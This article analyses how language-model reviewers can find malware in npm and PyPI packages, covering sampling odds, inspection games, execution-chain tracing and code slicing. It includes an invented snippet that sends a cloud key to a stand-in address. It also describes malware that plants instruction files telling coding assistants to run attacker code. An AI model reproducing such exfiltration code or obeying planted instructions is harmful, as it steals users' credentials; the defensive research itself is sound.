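More kinds of metadata would catch some of these, but not an attack in a package whose metadata looks ordinary. Guo and colleagues found malicious code in index.js in 47% of the malicious packages, and many harmless packages also have a file with that name. If a package has a plausible description, no install script and no unusual files, a reviewer has no reason to read a small index.js early, but still has to read it before calling the package harmless.

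## Does it help to read only a sample of the files?

A reviewer who chooses files by their metadata has no reason to open an ordinary-looking file early, and with a limited budget may never reach it. Picking files at random instead gives every file the same chance of being read. This works well for measuring how common malicious files are, but badly for finding a single payload.

### What a random sample finds

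Suppose a repository has N files, of which m are malicious, and the reviewer reads n different files picked at random. If C(a, b) is the number of ways to choose b items from a, there are C(N, n) possible samples, and C(N − m, n) of them contain no malicious file. The chance of reading at least one malicious file is therefore

1 − C(N − m, n) / C(N, n)

If a reviewer reads a random sample of 460 files from a repository of 10,000, and 100 of the 10,000 are malicious, the chance of reading at least one malicious file is about 99%. If only one file is malicious, the formula reduces to n/N (460/10,000), and the chance is 4.6%.

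The 99% chance depends almost entirely on the share of files that are malicious. In a repository of a million files with the same 1% malicious, a sample of 460 would still include at least one malicious file 99% of the time. If only one file is malicious, the chance of reading it equals the share of files the reviewer reads, so it falls to 0.046% in the larger repository.

Sampling therefore works well for estimating how common something is. If 20% of the files were obfuscated, a sample of 460 files would usually give a figure between 16% and 24%, however large the repository. But a clean sample is weak evidence that a repository is safe. If 63 of the 10,000 files were malicious, about one in 20 samples of that size would contain none of them.

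The model must also recognise malicious code when it reads it. If it does so with probability d, the chance of detecting a single malicious file is n/N × d, or 4.1% when d is 0.9. With 100 malicious files, the sample usually includes several, and the model detects at least one over 98% of the time if its mistakes are independent. If the files are copies of each other and the model recognises either all or none of them, the figure is 89%.

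False alarms add up across files just as they do across chunks. At an error rate of 0.5% per file, a reviewer that flags a repository whenever it flags any one file could flag up to 90% of harmless repositories, while finding a single payload only 4.1% of the time.

### Repeating the sample

A reviewer could draw a new sample at every scan. The chance that s independent samples all miss the one malicious file is (1 − 0.046)ˢ. This first drops below one half when s is 15, so about 15 samples give an even chance of reading the file.

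In a repository of 10,000 files, independent samples are inefficient because they overlap. They take about 6,900 file readings to give an even chance of reading the malicious file, but reading 5,000 different files would give the same chance. If the reviewer kept a list of files already read and never repeated one, 6,900 readings would give a 69% chance. Reaching 99% with independent samples takes 98 of them, or about 45,000 readings.

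Repeated sampling is more useful against a campaign that puts the same payload in many packages. If the campaign reached 500 packages, a model with a 4.6% chance of reading the payload in each would read it in about 23 of them. Once the model recognises one copy, ordinary software can search every other package for the same code. This doesn't protect people who have already installed an infected package, and the search may fail if the attacker alters each copy.

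The odds also change if the reviewer samples by size instead of by file. In executable-stories-demo, a reviewer that cut the code into equal chunks and picked one at random would get part of the 4.5 MB payload almost 99% of the time. The same method would do badly on llm-oracle, where the readable code that launches the disguised program is only about one byte in 6,300.

### Choosing files as a game

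The sampling formula treats the payload's location as fixed in advance, but an attacker who knows how the reviewer chooses files can put the payload in one that won't be read. If the reviewer always reads only the first 50 files, a payload in any other file goes unread, and c is zero. The rebuilt SocketAI workflow, with its limit of 20 files per package, missed payloads in this way even though the attackers probably didn't know about the limit.

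An attacker can't anticipate a random choice in this way. *Being hunted how randomness can help* (Lidbetter, 2015) gives the example of a fugitive who can hide in either Edinburgh or Glasgow. If the hunter has time to search only one city and chooses it by tossing a coin, he catches her half the time wherever she hides. But if she can predict which city he will search, she can always escape.

The same reasoning works for any number of hiding places. If there are k equally good places and the reviewer can read n of them, picking n at random gives it an n/k chance of reading the payload, wherever the attacker hides it. The reviewer can't guarantee a better chance, because an attacker who picks a place at random limits every reading strategy to n/k.

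Reducing the number of places where the payload could be (k) usually helps more than reading more of them (n). With 10,000 places, going from 460 reads to 500 raises the guaranteed chance of reading the payload from 4.6% to 5%. With 460 reads, cutting the places to 1,000 raises that chance to 46%, and cutting them to 460 makes it certain. One way to reduce k is to rule out code that never runs.

Some files are better hiding places than others, because a model is less likely to recognise a payload in them. Suppose there are ten files, and d, the chance that the model recognises a payload in a file it reads, is 0.9 for nine of them but 0.3 for the tenth, which is obfuscated. If the reviewer can read two files, its best policy is to read the obfuscated file half the time and each of the others a sixth of the time. The chance of detection is then 15% wherever the payload is. The obfuscated file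 is read most often because it would otherwise be the best place to hide the payload.

With four reads, the reviewer reads the obfuscated file every time, and the chance of detection is 30%. More reads don't raise the guaranteed chance of detection, because the attacker can use the obfuscated file. *Succession of hide-seek and pursuit-evasion at heterogeneous locations* (2014), which applies search games to predators and prey, identifies a similar threshold. Above a certain number of looks, the prey does best in the place where it is most likely to escape once spotted. A reviewer beyond that threshold should spend money on a better model, or on running the code in isolation, before paying for more reads.

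An agent's choice of files also varies from run to run, but this variation does not provide the n/k guarantee, because the agent tends to open files that look relevant. A dull-looking file may have almost no chance of being opened in any run.

### Whether spot checks deter attackers

Random checks on a few passengers can keep most people from travelling without a ticket. Game theorists study such checks as inspection games, in which an inspector with limited resources faces another party with an incentive to break the rules. *Recursive Inspection Games* (von Stengel, 2014) lists arms control, tax audits and fare evasion among the applications.

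*Finite Population Dynamics Resolve the Central Paradox of the Inspection Game* (2025) sets out the basic inspection game. An offender gains g and pays a penalty p if inspected. In the game's only equilibrium, where neither side can gain by changing strategy alone, both sides randomise. The inspector checks with probability g/p, the rate at which offending just stops being worthwhile. With a $3 fare and a $100 fine, that is 3%.

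The same calculation is much less favourable to spot checks for malware. If the reviewer stops a package, the attacker loses the expected gain and perhaps an account, so p is only a little more than g. If the account is worth a tenth of the gain, the required inspection rate is 1/1.1, or 91%, assuming every inspection succeeds. With d at 0.9, even reading every payload would give only a 90% chance of detection, which is too low to deter. Random spot checks deter fare evasion mainly because the fine is much larger than the fare, and a registry cannot impose a comparable fine.

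von Stengel analyses a version played over time, which the mathematician Melvin Dresher introduced. The inspector has a limited number of inspections to spread over a larger number of periods, and the other party breaks the rules in at most one of them. It could describe a reviewer that can afford to read five of a package's next ten releases. In von Stengel's solution, if being caught costs the attacker nothing beyond the lost prize, the attack succeeds half the time, just as the n/k rule implies. If being caught costs as much as success would bring, the attacker's expected gain falls from 50% of the prize to about 20%.

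That game ends when the inspector detects a violation, which von Stengel considers realistic for arms control. On a public registry, however, an attacker who is caught can open another account and try again. If each attempt has a 50% chance of getting through, the attacker needs two attempts on average, unless the reviewer stores what it found the first time and recognises it when it is resubmitted.

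In von Stengel's model of "inspector leadership", the inspector commits to a random schedule in advance. The other party then obeys the rules as long as inspections remain, and the inspector does better than without the commitment. This result depends on a real penalty, but it suggests that a reviewer can publish what share of files it reads at random. Only the choice of files has to stay unpredictable, so the reviewer should make it after the package arrives.

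### Letting a cheap pass choose

Random selection ignores any information that ordinary software could extract from the files. Ranked selection starts with a pass that takes little compute and scores all the code, and the model then reads only the code that scores highest. When EMPHunter ranked 112 packages, one of them malicious, by their install scripts, the malicious package was in the top ten 80% of the time, compared with 9% for a random choice of ten.

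Gao, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *Efficient Code Analysis via Graph-Guided Large Language Models*, apply the idea inside Python packages. Their system, GMLLM, works in four steps:

1. Ordinary software parses every Python file into a graph. The nodes are files, classes and functions, and the edges record which of them define, call or build on which others.
2. The software marks each node that matches a rule for sensitive behaviour, such as network access. A language model wrote most of these rules in advance.
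3. A small neural network scores the graph. It learnt from packages labelled only as malicious or harmless, so nobody had to mark the malicious lines. A further calculation, which takes about ten seconds per package, estimates how much each edge contributed to a malicious score.
4. GPT-4o receives the 20 edges that contributed most, with the nodes they connect, and gives a verdict.

Gao and colleagues tested the system on a collection with 1,659 malicious packages, 461 of them larger than 10 KB:

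| | GPT-4o alone | GMLLM with GPT-4o |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious packages over 10 KB detected | 67.3% | 87.2% |
| Average tokens, packages over 10 KB | 251,002 | 640 |
| Accuracy, all packages | 90.4% | 95.6% |

The average large package was about twice the size of GPT-4o's context window, and the researchers did not split the input. Some of the gain therefore probably comes from giving GPT-4o code that would not otherwise have fit, and some from removing harmless code. The graph network on its own reached 92.2% accuracy, better than GPT-4o alone, so it did much of the detection as well as selecting the code.

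The size of the selection mattered less than the ranking. Accuracy was 93.0% with 10 edges, 95.6% with 20 and 94.9% with 50. Going from 20 to 50 edges raised the share of malicious packages detected from 95.3% to 96.0%, but lowered the share of harmless packages cleared from 95.9% to 94.0%. A selection that is too small can leave out the payload, as can happen when a preprocessor keeps only three code units.

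These results have several weaknesses. Gao and colleagues did not try 20 random edges, so the test doesn't show how much the ranking contributed. They also used the test results to decide when to stop training, which can make accuracy look better than it would be on new packages. It isn't clear how much code GPT-4o received. The main description includes the source code of the selected nodes, but the prompt in the appendix describes only names and call relationships. The average of 640 tokens fits the prompt's description better. In one sample verdict, the model cites functions called steal_cookies and steal_passwords, names that an attacker could easily change.

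The graph also covers only Python source. A program in another format, like the one in llm-oracle, would never enter the ranking.

### Rules that run over all the code

*Automatically Generating Rules of Malicious Software Packages via Large Language Model* (Zhang, Du and colleagues, 2025) describes RuleLLM, a system that uses a language model at an earlier stage, to read known malware and write detection rules. Ordinary scanners can then run these rules over any amount of code without using tokens.

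The researchers started with 1,633 distinct malicious PyPI packages and grouped similar pieces of their code. GPT-4o received several similar pieces at a time, split into blocks of at most about 4,000 characters, and wrote a rule for what they had in common. A second call refined and merged the rules. An agent compiled each one, with up to five attempts to fix any errors. This produced 452 rules for YARA, which searches for patterns in text and binary files, and 311 for Semgrep, which searches for patterns in the structure of code.

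RuleLLM's rules detected 91.8% of the malicious packages, compared with 23.4% for existing YARA rules and 32.0% for existing Semgrep rules, most of which were written for other kinds of threat. The paper describes no separate test set for this comparison, so RuleLLM may have written its rules from the same packages it was tested on. In another test, rules written from two packages in each group of similar malware detected 90.3% of the remaining packages, though these were by design similar to the ones the model had read.

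False alarms are the main problem. The published precision of 85.2% is high partly because more than three-quarters of the packages in the test were malicious. The figures imply that the rules flagged about 260 of the 500 harmless packages. If one new package in 1,000 is malicious, a match at those rates raises the chance that a package is malicious from 0.1% to only 0.18%. Simply having an install script raises it to about 3.6%. The harmless packages were popular and averaged 3,052 lines, compared with 424 for the malware, so the false-alarm rate might be lower for typical packages.

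RuleLLM's output is therefore more useful for ranking than for verdicts, and its rules should not all count equally. Precision was about 98% for 278 of the YARA rules, but 65 others matched no malicious package. About 40 Semgrep rules had a precision close to zero. A reviewer could give more weight to matches from the reliable rules, as long as it measured their reliability on packages not used to write them.

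### Combining ranked and random reading

A ranking is another fixed rule that an attacker can plan around. Zhang, Du and colleagues have published their rules, so anyone can check whether a file matches them. A reviewer that reads the top-ranked files could also read a random sample of the rest, so that every file has some chance of being read.

Let q be the chance that the payload is among the t top-ranked files. If the reviewer also reads r random files from the remaining N − t, the chance of reading the payload is

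q + (1 − q) × r / (N − t)

The next table applies this to 10,000 files and 460 reads, assuming that an ordinary payload ranks in the top 400 files 80% of the time and never between 401 and 460. The last column shows the case where an attacker has made the payload rank low.

| Files read | Ordinary payload | Payload made to rank low |
|---|---|---|
| 460 random | 4.6% | 4.6% |
| 460 top-ranked | 80% | 0% |
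| 400 top-ranked, 60 random | 80.1% | 0.6% |

Setting aside 60 reads for random files loses little here, but it also gains little. If even a few payloads ranked between 401 and 460, reading those 60 files would catch more than reading 60 at random. Random reading helps more when fewer files remain. If the reviewer could first narrow the 10,000 files to 600, the 60 random reads would cover 30% of the 200 files outside the top 400.

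The optimal policy in some search games similarly mixes fixed and random choices. In one example from *Hide-and-Seek Game with Capacitated Locations and Imperfect Detection* (2023), a searcher has four inspections for six places in which an opponent has hidden ten items. The searcher always inspects two of the places, inspects three others with probabilities from 0.24 to 0.96, and never inspects the sixth, where the opponent hides two items on average. That loss is acceptable when the goal is to find as many items as possible, but an attack on a codebase can succeed with one unread payload, so a code reviewer's random sample should give every file outside the top ranks a chance of being read.

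Random reading is more valuable as a check on the ranking. Suppose a reviewer reads 60 randomly chosen low-ranked files in each of 1,000 repositories, and one low-ranked file in 10,000 is malicious. It would read about six malicious files among the 60,000, with less than a 1% chance of reading none. Even a false-alarm rate of 0.03% per file would add about 18 false alarms to investigate. But the operator would get a rough estimate of how much malware the ranking leaves unread and examples for improving it, neither of which comes from reading only top-ranked files.

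## Is it enough to follow the code that will run?

A reviewer could narrow its search for a payload by reading only the code that will run. The argument for this has three premises:

1. A payload has to run to do harm.
2. Code can start running only from a limited set of entry points.
3. A reviewer that follows every path from those entry points will reach the payload.

If all three are true, c is 1 even when most of the package goes unread.

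The first premise is true only if "run" has a broad meaning, because a text file that tells an AI coding assistant to execute a command can do harm even though no machine runs the file as a program. The second premise holds for any given platform, but the platform determines which files start automatically, and a reviewer's list of them may be incomplete. The third is the weakest, because a program can compute what to load while it is running.

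### The procedure

The reviewer first lists everything that can start the package's code:

| Starting point | npm | PyPI |
|---|---|---|
| Installation | Install scripts in the manifest | setup.py |
| Build | Build files such as binding.gyp | setup.py or another build script |
| Import | The main file, and any other file a program can import | \_\_init\_\_.py and any other module |
| Command line | Commands declared in the manifest | Commands declared in the metadata |

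The reviewer then opens each of these files and records every other file that the code loads, runs or decodes. It includes decoded files because a file that looks like plain data can contain an encoded program. It adds the new files to the list and checks them the same way until it finds no more. It never opens the same file twice, so the process ends even if two files load each other. If it can't tell which file a line refers to, it should record that line as unresolved, because that file could contain the payload.

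### A chain of three files

OSV's *MAL-2026-4278* (2026), an entry in a public database of software vulnerabilities and malware, describes ten npm packages that one account published for developers of AI tools. One of them, llm-context-compressor, was advertised as a way to shorten text to fit a model's context window.

The execution chain has three files. The manifest, package.json, declares a script that runs after installation and starts lib/setup.js, which then starts lib/worker.js. That file searches the disk for private keys, cloud credentials and passwords. A reviewer that follows the procedure can find the theft by opening only these three files. A reviewer that started with the file that applications import might have opened neither lib/setup.js nor lib/worker.js.

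The chain continues outside the package, because the worker downloads settings from the attacker's web page, including where to send the stolen data and how to search. A reviewer can't find these settings in the package, and the attacker can change them after the review. That matters little here, because worker.js already contains backup addresses and the code that steals the data.

The worker also creates new entry points on the victim's machine. It adds scripts that Git runs at certain moments and commands that run whenever the user opens a terminal. In project folders, it leaves instruction files for coding assistants such as Claude Code and Cursor. These files are disguised as a company security standard, and an assistant that follows them will run the attacker's code and spread it further.

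Version 1.5.0 of the package contains another file, lib/trap-core.js, with about 1,000 lines. Amazon's scanning service, Inspector, cites evidence of malice from line 28 to line 1,024. An agent that read only the first 100 lines, the default in LangChain's tool, would see some file checks and a network test but none of the code that sends data out. The database entry doesn't identify what loads trap-core.js, but Amazon advises treating it as malicious "regardless of how the module is reached".

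### CHASE

*CHASE*, published in January 2026, describes a system of the same name that follows part of this procedure for PyPI packages. A supervisor agent, running on the open model Qwen3 32B, reads the source code, writes a plan and assigns tasks to two worker agents. One worker decodes or decrypts hidden text and can run fragments of code in isolation. The other downloads remote files and looks up suspicious web addresses. Both workers use Qwen3 8B, a smaller model that is about three times as fast.

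The supervisor revises its plan after each result. In one package, setup.py contained an encoded Windows command. The first worker decoded it and found a Dropbox address, so the supervisor dropped its remaining work on the command and had the second worker investigate the address. Seven security vendors had already flagged the address.

A fixed rule determines which files the system reads: setup.py, \_\_init\_\_.py and the Python files that \_\_init\_\_.py imports. The researchers chose these files partly because reading whole packages took too much computing power, and partly because an earlier study had found that 87.6% of malicious PyPI packages act when installed or imported.

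They tested it on 500 malicious packages and 2,500 harmless ones, with a limit of 20 minutes per package:

| | Judged malicious | Judged harmless | Timed out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious packages | 492 | 0 | 8 |
| Harmless packages | 2 | 2,473 | 25 |

The system detected 98.4% of the malicious packages, counting timeouts as misses, and wrongly flagged 0.08% of the harmless packages it finished. It finished all the packages that had timed out within two more attempts and classified them correctly. The median analysis took about four and a half minutes, but the server ran ten at a time on a single GPU, so it could process roughly 3,000 packages a day.

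These results are better than the reading rule would lead us to expect. If 12.4% of the 500 malicious packages had kept their payloads outside the files the system read, that would have been 62 packages, yet the system missed none of those it finished reviewing. Either the sample contained few such packages, or \_\_init\_\_.py imported the files where those payloads were. The test therefore provides little evidence about whether the system can catch payloads outside the files it reads. The system could also look up addresses from attacks that were already public, as in the Dropbox case. Such a lookup may find nothing if the reviewer sees the package minutes after its release.

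One of the two false alarms occurred partly because the rule missed a link between files. A harmless setup.py opened version.py and executed its text to get the version number. Since setup.py didn't import version.py, the rule didn't include that file, and the system flagged the package as suspicious partly because it couldn't read it. In their PyPI study, Guo and colleagues found that harmless code of this kind caused many of GuardDog's false alarms. An attacker could just as easily put a payload in version.py, and a reviewer that opened the file could tell whether it contained one.

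### An agent or a program to find the next file

Mercury's agents had read different files on different runs, so its engineers used ordinary software to find the next file instead. They compiled their Haskell code with an option that records where each function is and which others it refers to, then turned these records into a graph. The software starts from the function that handles a web route and collects every function that one refers to, then every function those refer to, until there are no more. It copies their text into a single file for the model. Tracing the whole codebase this way takes about five minutes.

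The model then gets the same code every time, so the engineers could test prompts fairly. They checked whether the model found known flaws in old versions of the code. The full scan flagged 13.6% of the routes, and roughly half the findings were real security problems or code that the engineers were willing to change.

The method is harder to apply to malware. Mercury's graph contains only the company's own code and only the references the compiler could resolve. Mercury could also build its code safely, but building an unknown package may run an attacker's code, so a reviewer would have to build it in isolation.

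The graph also has to start in the right place. ProfMal, a tool in the npm study by Guo and colleagues, builds a graph of a package's behaviour and runs the package to fill in calls it can't work out from the code. It still missed 1,448 of the 6,420 malicious packages. Guo and colleagues attribute this to attacks confined to install scripts, which leave little for a graph to capture. In llm-context-compressor, too, the first link is from a command in package.json to a JavaScript file, so a graph of JavaScript references alone would miss it.

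An agent handles such links better, because it can interpret a shell command or decode a string. The two methods work well together if software first builds as much of the chain as it can and an agent then works on the unresolved links. The agent should be able to add files to the list but not remove them, so that if it stops early, the reviewer loses only the files it would have added.

### When payloads run

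Most known malware runs as early as possible. According to GitHub (2026), attackers use install scripts to spread their malware quickly. Of the new malicious packages that Guo and colleagues found on PyPI between March and June 2024, 94.4% acted during installation, 4.2% on import and the rest later. Their detector reads only Python files, so it may have missed packages that start in other ways. *Unveiling Malicious Logic* (2025) catalogues signs of malice in 370 Python packages, including 155 cases of code that runs on installation and 25 of code that runs on import.

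These figures predate npm version 12, which does not run the install scripts of dependencies unless a project explicitly allows them. The same default blocks the automatic build that launched the payload in ai-sdk-ollama. GitHub announced the change in June 2026 (*Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12*, 2026) and confirmed in July that version 12 was generally available with the new defaults (*npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation*, 2026).

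The security company Checkmarx points out that importing a package still runs any code outside its functions, and expects attackers to move their payloads there. In mid-July, Microsoft (2026) described an attack on the AsyncAPI packages that worked this way. The attacker put a heavily obfuscated loader in one source file of each package. The loader ran when a program imported the package, so blocking install scripts had no effect. We can't tell from one attack whether the new default is changing attackers' habits.

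Such a shift would mean reading more code to follow the chain. In llm-context-compressor, the install script leads to two files. But importing a library can load most of its code, so a reviewer that starts from the import may have to read nearly everything.

Install scripts still belong on the list of entry points because projects can allow them and older versions of npm run them automatically. In Infosecurity Magazine's *GitHub to Update npm to Thwart Software Supply Chain Attacks* (2026), the researcher Paul McCarty warns that many developers will approve blocked scripts without checking them, just to get their software to build. He also expects developers of harmless packages to adopt workarounds that look like malware.

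### An entry point that nobody listed

LiteLLM is a Python package that connects applications to many different language models. On March 24, 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of it, according to Trend Micro's *Your AI Gateway Was a Backdoor*. The first, 1.82.7, had its payload in proxy_server.py, which runs when a program imports LiteLLM's proxy module. A reviewer that started from the package's main \_\_init\_\_.py would reach this file only if the imports led to it. The procedure therefore treats every module that a program can import as an entry point.

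Version 1.82.8 followed 13 minutes later. It kept the first payload and added a 34,628-byte file called litellm_init.pth. Python reads .pth files whenever it starts. These files mainly list where to look for modules, but Python also executes any line in them that begins with "import", as StepSecurity explains. The payload therefore ran whenever Python started on the machine, even if no program imported LiteLLM. According to Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM*, it ran even when the installer or a code editor started Python in the background.

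A reviewer that read only setup.py and \_\_init\_\_.py would not have opened the file. A reviewer that collected all the Python scripts in the package, as the models in *LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection* did, would also have missed it, because the file doesn't have the usual .py ending. The package's own list of contents included the file, so checking that list could have caught it.

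The payload was discovered by accident, when a mistake in it started so many processes that machines crashed. A researcher whose coding tool had installed LiteLLM as a dependency investigated the crashes. PyPI quarantined both versions after about three hours. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) announced a clean release on March 30.

Python's developers have known about this risk for years. Recent versions of Python skip hidden .pth files, but a proposal to stop all .pth files from executing code remains unresolved. A reviewer can add .pth files to its list, but the next attack may use a feature that isn't on it. It is safer for the reviewer to open any file whose type it doesn't recognise, and to leave the file out only after establishing what the platform does with it.

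### Links that reading does not resolve

Even with a complete list of entry points, a reviewer can fail to reach the malicious code. PyGuard, the system from the PyPI study by Guo and colleagues, checks every Python file in a package and missed only 19 of more than 2,000 malicious packages in its main test. All 19 payloads were outside the code it analyses: eight were in a dependency, six were in code that the package installed from elsewhere when it ran, and five were in files that weren't Python. The test packages came from the same collection that the researchers used to build PyGuard, so it may miss more in new attacks.

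Dependencies can make the chain very long. Guo and colleagues' npm study cites an estimate that installing the average npm package means implicitly trusting 79 others. If each had 5,000 tokens, the median for popular packages, following all of them would add about 400,000 tokens to one review. A reviewer could skip most of that reading if every exact version in the chain already had a stored verdict.

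Code that a package downloads later is harder to review. The AsyncAPI loader fetched its second stage from IPFS, a network for sharing files, so a reviewer could read every line of the package without seeing that stage. CHASE can download such files, but an attacker can serve harmless code to a scanner and a payload to everyone else, or swap the file afterwards. The LiteLLM payload installed a program that checked the attacker's server for new code every 50 minutes. In these cases the reviewer has to judge the step that downloads and runs the code, which can cause false alarms because harmless packages download files too.

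A program can also compute the name of the file or function it will use. In May, Microsoft (2026) described a campaign of 33 npm packages whose install script kept its web addresses and function names in a scrambled list and decoded them only while running. *CHASE* describes a Python package that decodes its payload, writes it to a new file and launches that file as a separate program. The competing detector MalGuard missed this package because the new file didn't exist when MalGuard built its graph. An agent that can decode the text has a better chance, but not when the code leads to a native program like the one in llm-oracle, because the readable part of the chain ends there.

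Dormant code is less of a problem for a reviewer that reads the package than for a system that runs it. The LiteLLM payload checked whether it was on one of GitHub's build machines and excluded certain regions, so a test run under the wrong conditions might show nothing. A model can read the code on both sides of a condition, but it could miss the payload if it assumes the condition will never be true and skips the code behind it. *Unveiling Malicious Logic* lists 70 cases of payloads that wait for a condition, so a reviewer should follow both branches unless it can prove that one is impossible.

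### When code can stay unread

A reviewer can safely leave a file unread if it knows all the entry points, has read everything they lead to, and has resolved every step that loads, runs or decodes something. Resolving a step doesn't always require an exact answer. For example, if a program computes the name of a file to load from its plugins folder, the reviewer can count every file in that folder as reachable.

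Other steps have no such limit. If the code executes text that it computes or downloads, or launches a native program, it could open any file in the package. The reviewer then can't rule out any file, and calling one "unreachable" means only that the reviewer found no path to it. The reviewer has to work out what the step does, read the rest of the package, or report that part of the package remains unread.

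For most past malware, a simple search along the chain would probably have been enough. Guo and colleagues found no evasion technique in 80.3% of the malicious npm packages they studied. But an attacker who expects a reviewer to follow the chain needs only one link that the reviewer can't resolve. This method is most useful for packages with plain, readable imports, where a reviewer can rule out documentation, examples and test data with some confidence, and least useful for obfuscated packages.

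A file that nothing in its own package loads may still run, because another package can often import it directly. The next version may also add a line that loads the file, and a comparison of the two versions would omit the file itself because it hadn't changed. If llm-context-compressor had contained trap-core.js without loading it, a reviewer following the chain could have skipped the file in that version. The reviewer should then have recorded the file as unread, so that a later review would open it as soon as any code referred to it.

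## Can the code be shortened before the model reads it?

Following the execution chain narrows a review to certain files, but one of those files may still be too large for the context window. Ordinary software can shorten it before the model reads it, by removing statements that are irrelevant to possible harm or by condensing long stretches of text. This can raise c, because more files fit, and d, because less harmless code surrounds the payload. But the software may also discard the payload before the model can read it.

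### Slicing a short program

A slice contains the statements of a program that can affect a chosen operation. The computer scientist Mark Weiser described the technique in a 1981 paper. In a search for malware, the chosen operation is a sink, which is an operation that can do harm, such as running a command or sending data over the network. A source is a place where the program obtains sensitive data, such as a password file. This invented program has one of each:

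```
1  const title = "Weather today";
2  const key = process.env.CLOUD_KEY;
3  const units = "celsius";
4  const packed = encode(key);
5  console.log(title, units);
6  if (isOnline()) {
7    send("https://example.com", packed);
8  }
```

Line 2 is the source, because it reads a cloud key from the machine's settings. Line 7 is the sink, because it sends `packed`. A slicer starts at line 7 and traces the data back through line 4, which makes `packed` from `key`, to line 2, where `key` comes from. It keeps those three lines. A slicer that also tracks conditions keeps the "if" around line 7. Either way, lines 1, 3 and 5 disappear, and the theft is easier to see. If the package defines `encode` in another file, that function belongs in the slice too.

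The trace can fail in real code. If the program assembles the name `send` from fragments while running, the slicer may not find a sink. JavaScript also delays much of its work. For example, a program might request a file and register a function to run when the contents arrive. No line visibly passes the contents to that function, so a simple trace stops there.

### Slicing npm packages

*Taint-Based Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection* (2025), a revised version of the slicing paper by Nguyen, Dang-Thi and colleagues, describes a slicer that can trace data backwards through such delayed calls. The slicer uses taint analysis, which marks data from a source as tainted and follows it to a sink. The researchers compared it with plain 500-token chunks and with a broader kind of slicing based on control flow, the order in which statements can run. They used DeepSeek-Coder-6.7B,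 a 6.7-billion-parameter model, on two consumer graphics cards.

| Input | Median tokens | Accuracy | Malicious packages detected | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 500-token chunks | 3,594 | 75.41% | 55.5% | 87.1% |
| Control-flow slices | 358 | 75.65% | 60.5% | 96.0% |
| Taint slices | 228 | 87.04% | 72.9% | 96.2% |

Precision is the share of flagged packages that were malicious. Taint slicing did best on every measure and cut the median input by 93.7%. That figure probably overstates the reduction, because the 3,594 tokens are for a whole package, while the slice figures appear to be for individual slices, and one package can produce several.

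The reported accuracies also don't quite match the detection and precision figures. The test had 1,453 malicious and 1,084 harmless packages, so those figures imply an accuracy of about 83% for taint slices, 76% for control-flow slices and 70% for chunks. An earlier version of the paper swaps the detection and precision figures, but that fits the reported accuracies even less well. Taint slicing beats plain chunks by more than 11 points on both the reported and the implied accuracies.

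Taint slicing probably did better than control-flow slicing because it removed more harmless code. In harmless packages, it kept 9.4% of the lines that mention a listed source or sink, compared with 15.9% for control-flow slicing. Both kept about 73% of such lines in malicious packages, so about a quarter did not reach the model even when the slicer worked.

### Empty slices

These results cover only 2,537 packages. Nguyen and colleagues started with 7,309 and first removed 1,336 with corrupt or empty archives. They then removed 131 malicious packages that contained only metadata or used none of the sensitive operations on their list. They gave the slicer three minutes for each of the remaining 5,842 packages, and it produced nothing for 3,305 of them, including 44% of the malicious packages and 67% of the harmless ones.

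An empty slice leaves the model with no code to read. The slicer may return one because no path runs from a source to a sink, because the program hides the path by computing names or generating code while it runs, or because the slicer ran out of time. If the reviewer treats all empty slices as harmless, it clears packages the model never read, and no error warns the operator.

Slicing can cause a reviewer to miss many malicious packages. The slicer produced non-empty slices for 1,453 of the 2,600 malicious packages it received (56%), and the model detected 72.9% of those. If empty slices count as harmless, the reviewer detects only 41% of the 2,600. Plain chunks, which leave no code out, detected 55.5% in the test. If that rate also held for the packages with empty slices, plain chunks would detect more malware overall than slicing, and a reviewer that used slices where it had them and chunks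 elsewhere would detect about 65%.

Nguyen and colleagues acknowledge this "survival bias". They write that a production system must run packages with empty slices in isolation, or have a language model undo the obfuscation before slicing them again.

Some slices are empty because the slicer's list of sinks is incomplete. A package might send data through a function in a third-party library, and a slicer that lists only JavaScript's built-in network functions would miss that call. MalTotal, a system by Zhao and colleagues, uses a language model to summarise what library functions do and identify those that perform sensitive operations. It stores the summaries, so it analyses each library only once. It then slices backwards from every sensitive call, following data, conditions and chains of function calls.

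On 2,168 repositories, MalTotal's slicing cut token use by 94% and cost from $86.25 to $5.19. Zhao and colleagues then scanned 120,000 GitHub repositories for $338 and found 564 previously unreported malicious ones. At the unsliced cost per repository, the scan would have cost almost $4,800. But the number of discoveries doesn't show how many malicious repositories the scan missed.

### The four steps of CASHEWS

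CASHEWS, the JavaScript preprocessor built by Noirot Ferrand and colleagues, deletes code more conservatively. Slicing is only the third of its four steps, and CASHEWS keeps the original code when the slicer's result is uncertain.

CASHEWS starts by decoding the code. It looks for known kinds of obfuscation, reverses them and searches the result again, because one layer may hide another. For example, the first round might join several short strings into one long encoded string, and the second might decode that string into a program. Some obfuscation tools hide text in a list that the program reshuffles when it starts. In those cases, CASHEWS runs only the start-up code, in isolation and for at most five seconds. Decoding stops when a round changes nothing or after 20 rounds.

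Decoding can change a verdict without making the code much shorter. One file of more than 8,000 tokens came from a package that supposedly connected an automation tool to Google Ads. DeepSeek V4 Flash first classified it as probably a legitimate commercial library. Decoding revealed that a function named `validateLicense` sent system information and licence credentials to a fixed web address, and the model then classified the file as malicious.

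In the second step, extraction, CASHEWS recognises the output of six common build tools and separates each bundle into its modules. It also extracts strings that are JavaScript programs. If a file is still large and contains neither bundled modules nor such strings, CASHEWS cuts it at natural boundaries in the code. It replaces each extracted piece, called a unit, with a label and puts the code below, under the same label.

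Slicing comes third. CASHEWS removes functions and classes that it can't reach from any starting point, then traces backwards from each sink and from everything the file makes available to other programs. If it can't tell which function a line will call, it keeps all the candidates. It also keeps the original code in any of these cases:

- It finds no sink.
- The code that leads to a sink can generate and run new code.
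- The code that leads to a sink loads another file.
- Sensitive data flows to a different sink that the slice would remove.
- The file is too complex to analyse within fixed limits.

The first of these rules deals with the empty slice. If CASHEWS finds no sink, the model still receives the code.

In the last step, CASHEWS abbreviates the code. It replaces very long names with short ones such as var_1 and cuts the middle out of long strings and lists, noting how much it removed from the longest ones. It keeps the first 48 and last 8 characters of a long web address, because the address may be evidence. For ai-sdk-ollama, this would reduce the payload's long list of numbers to a few numbers and a note of how much was removed. CASHEWS also strips comments, which would include the kind of reassuring ones that Cloudflare found in padded scripts.

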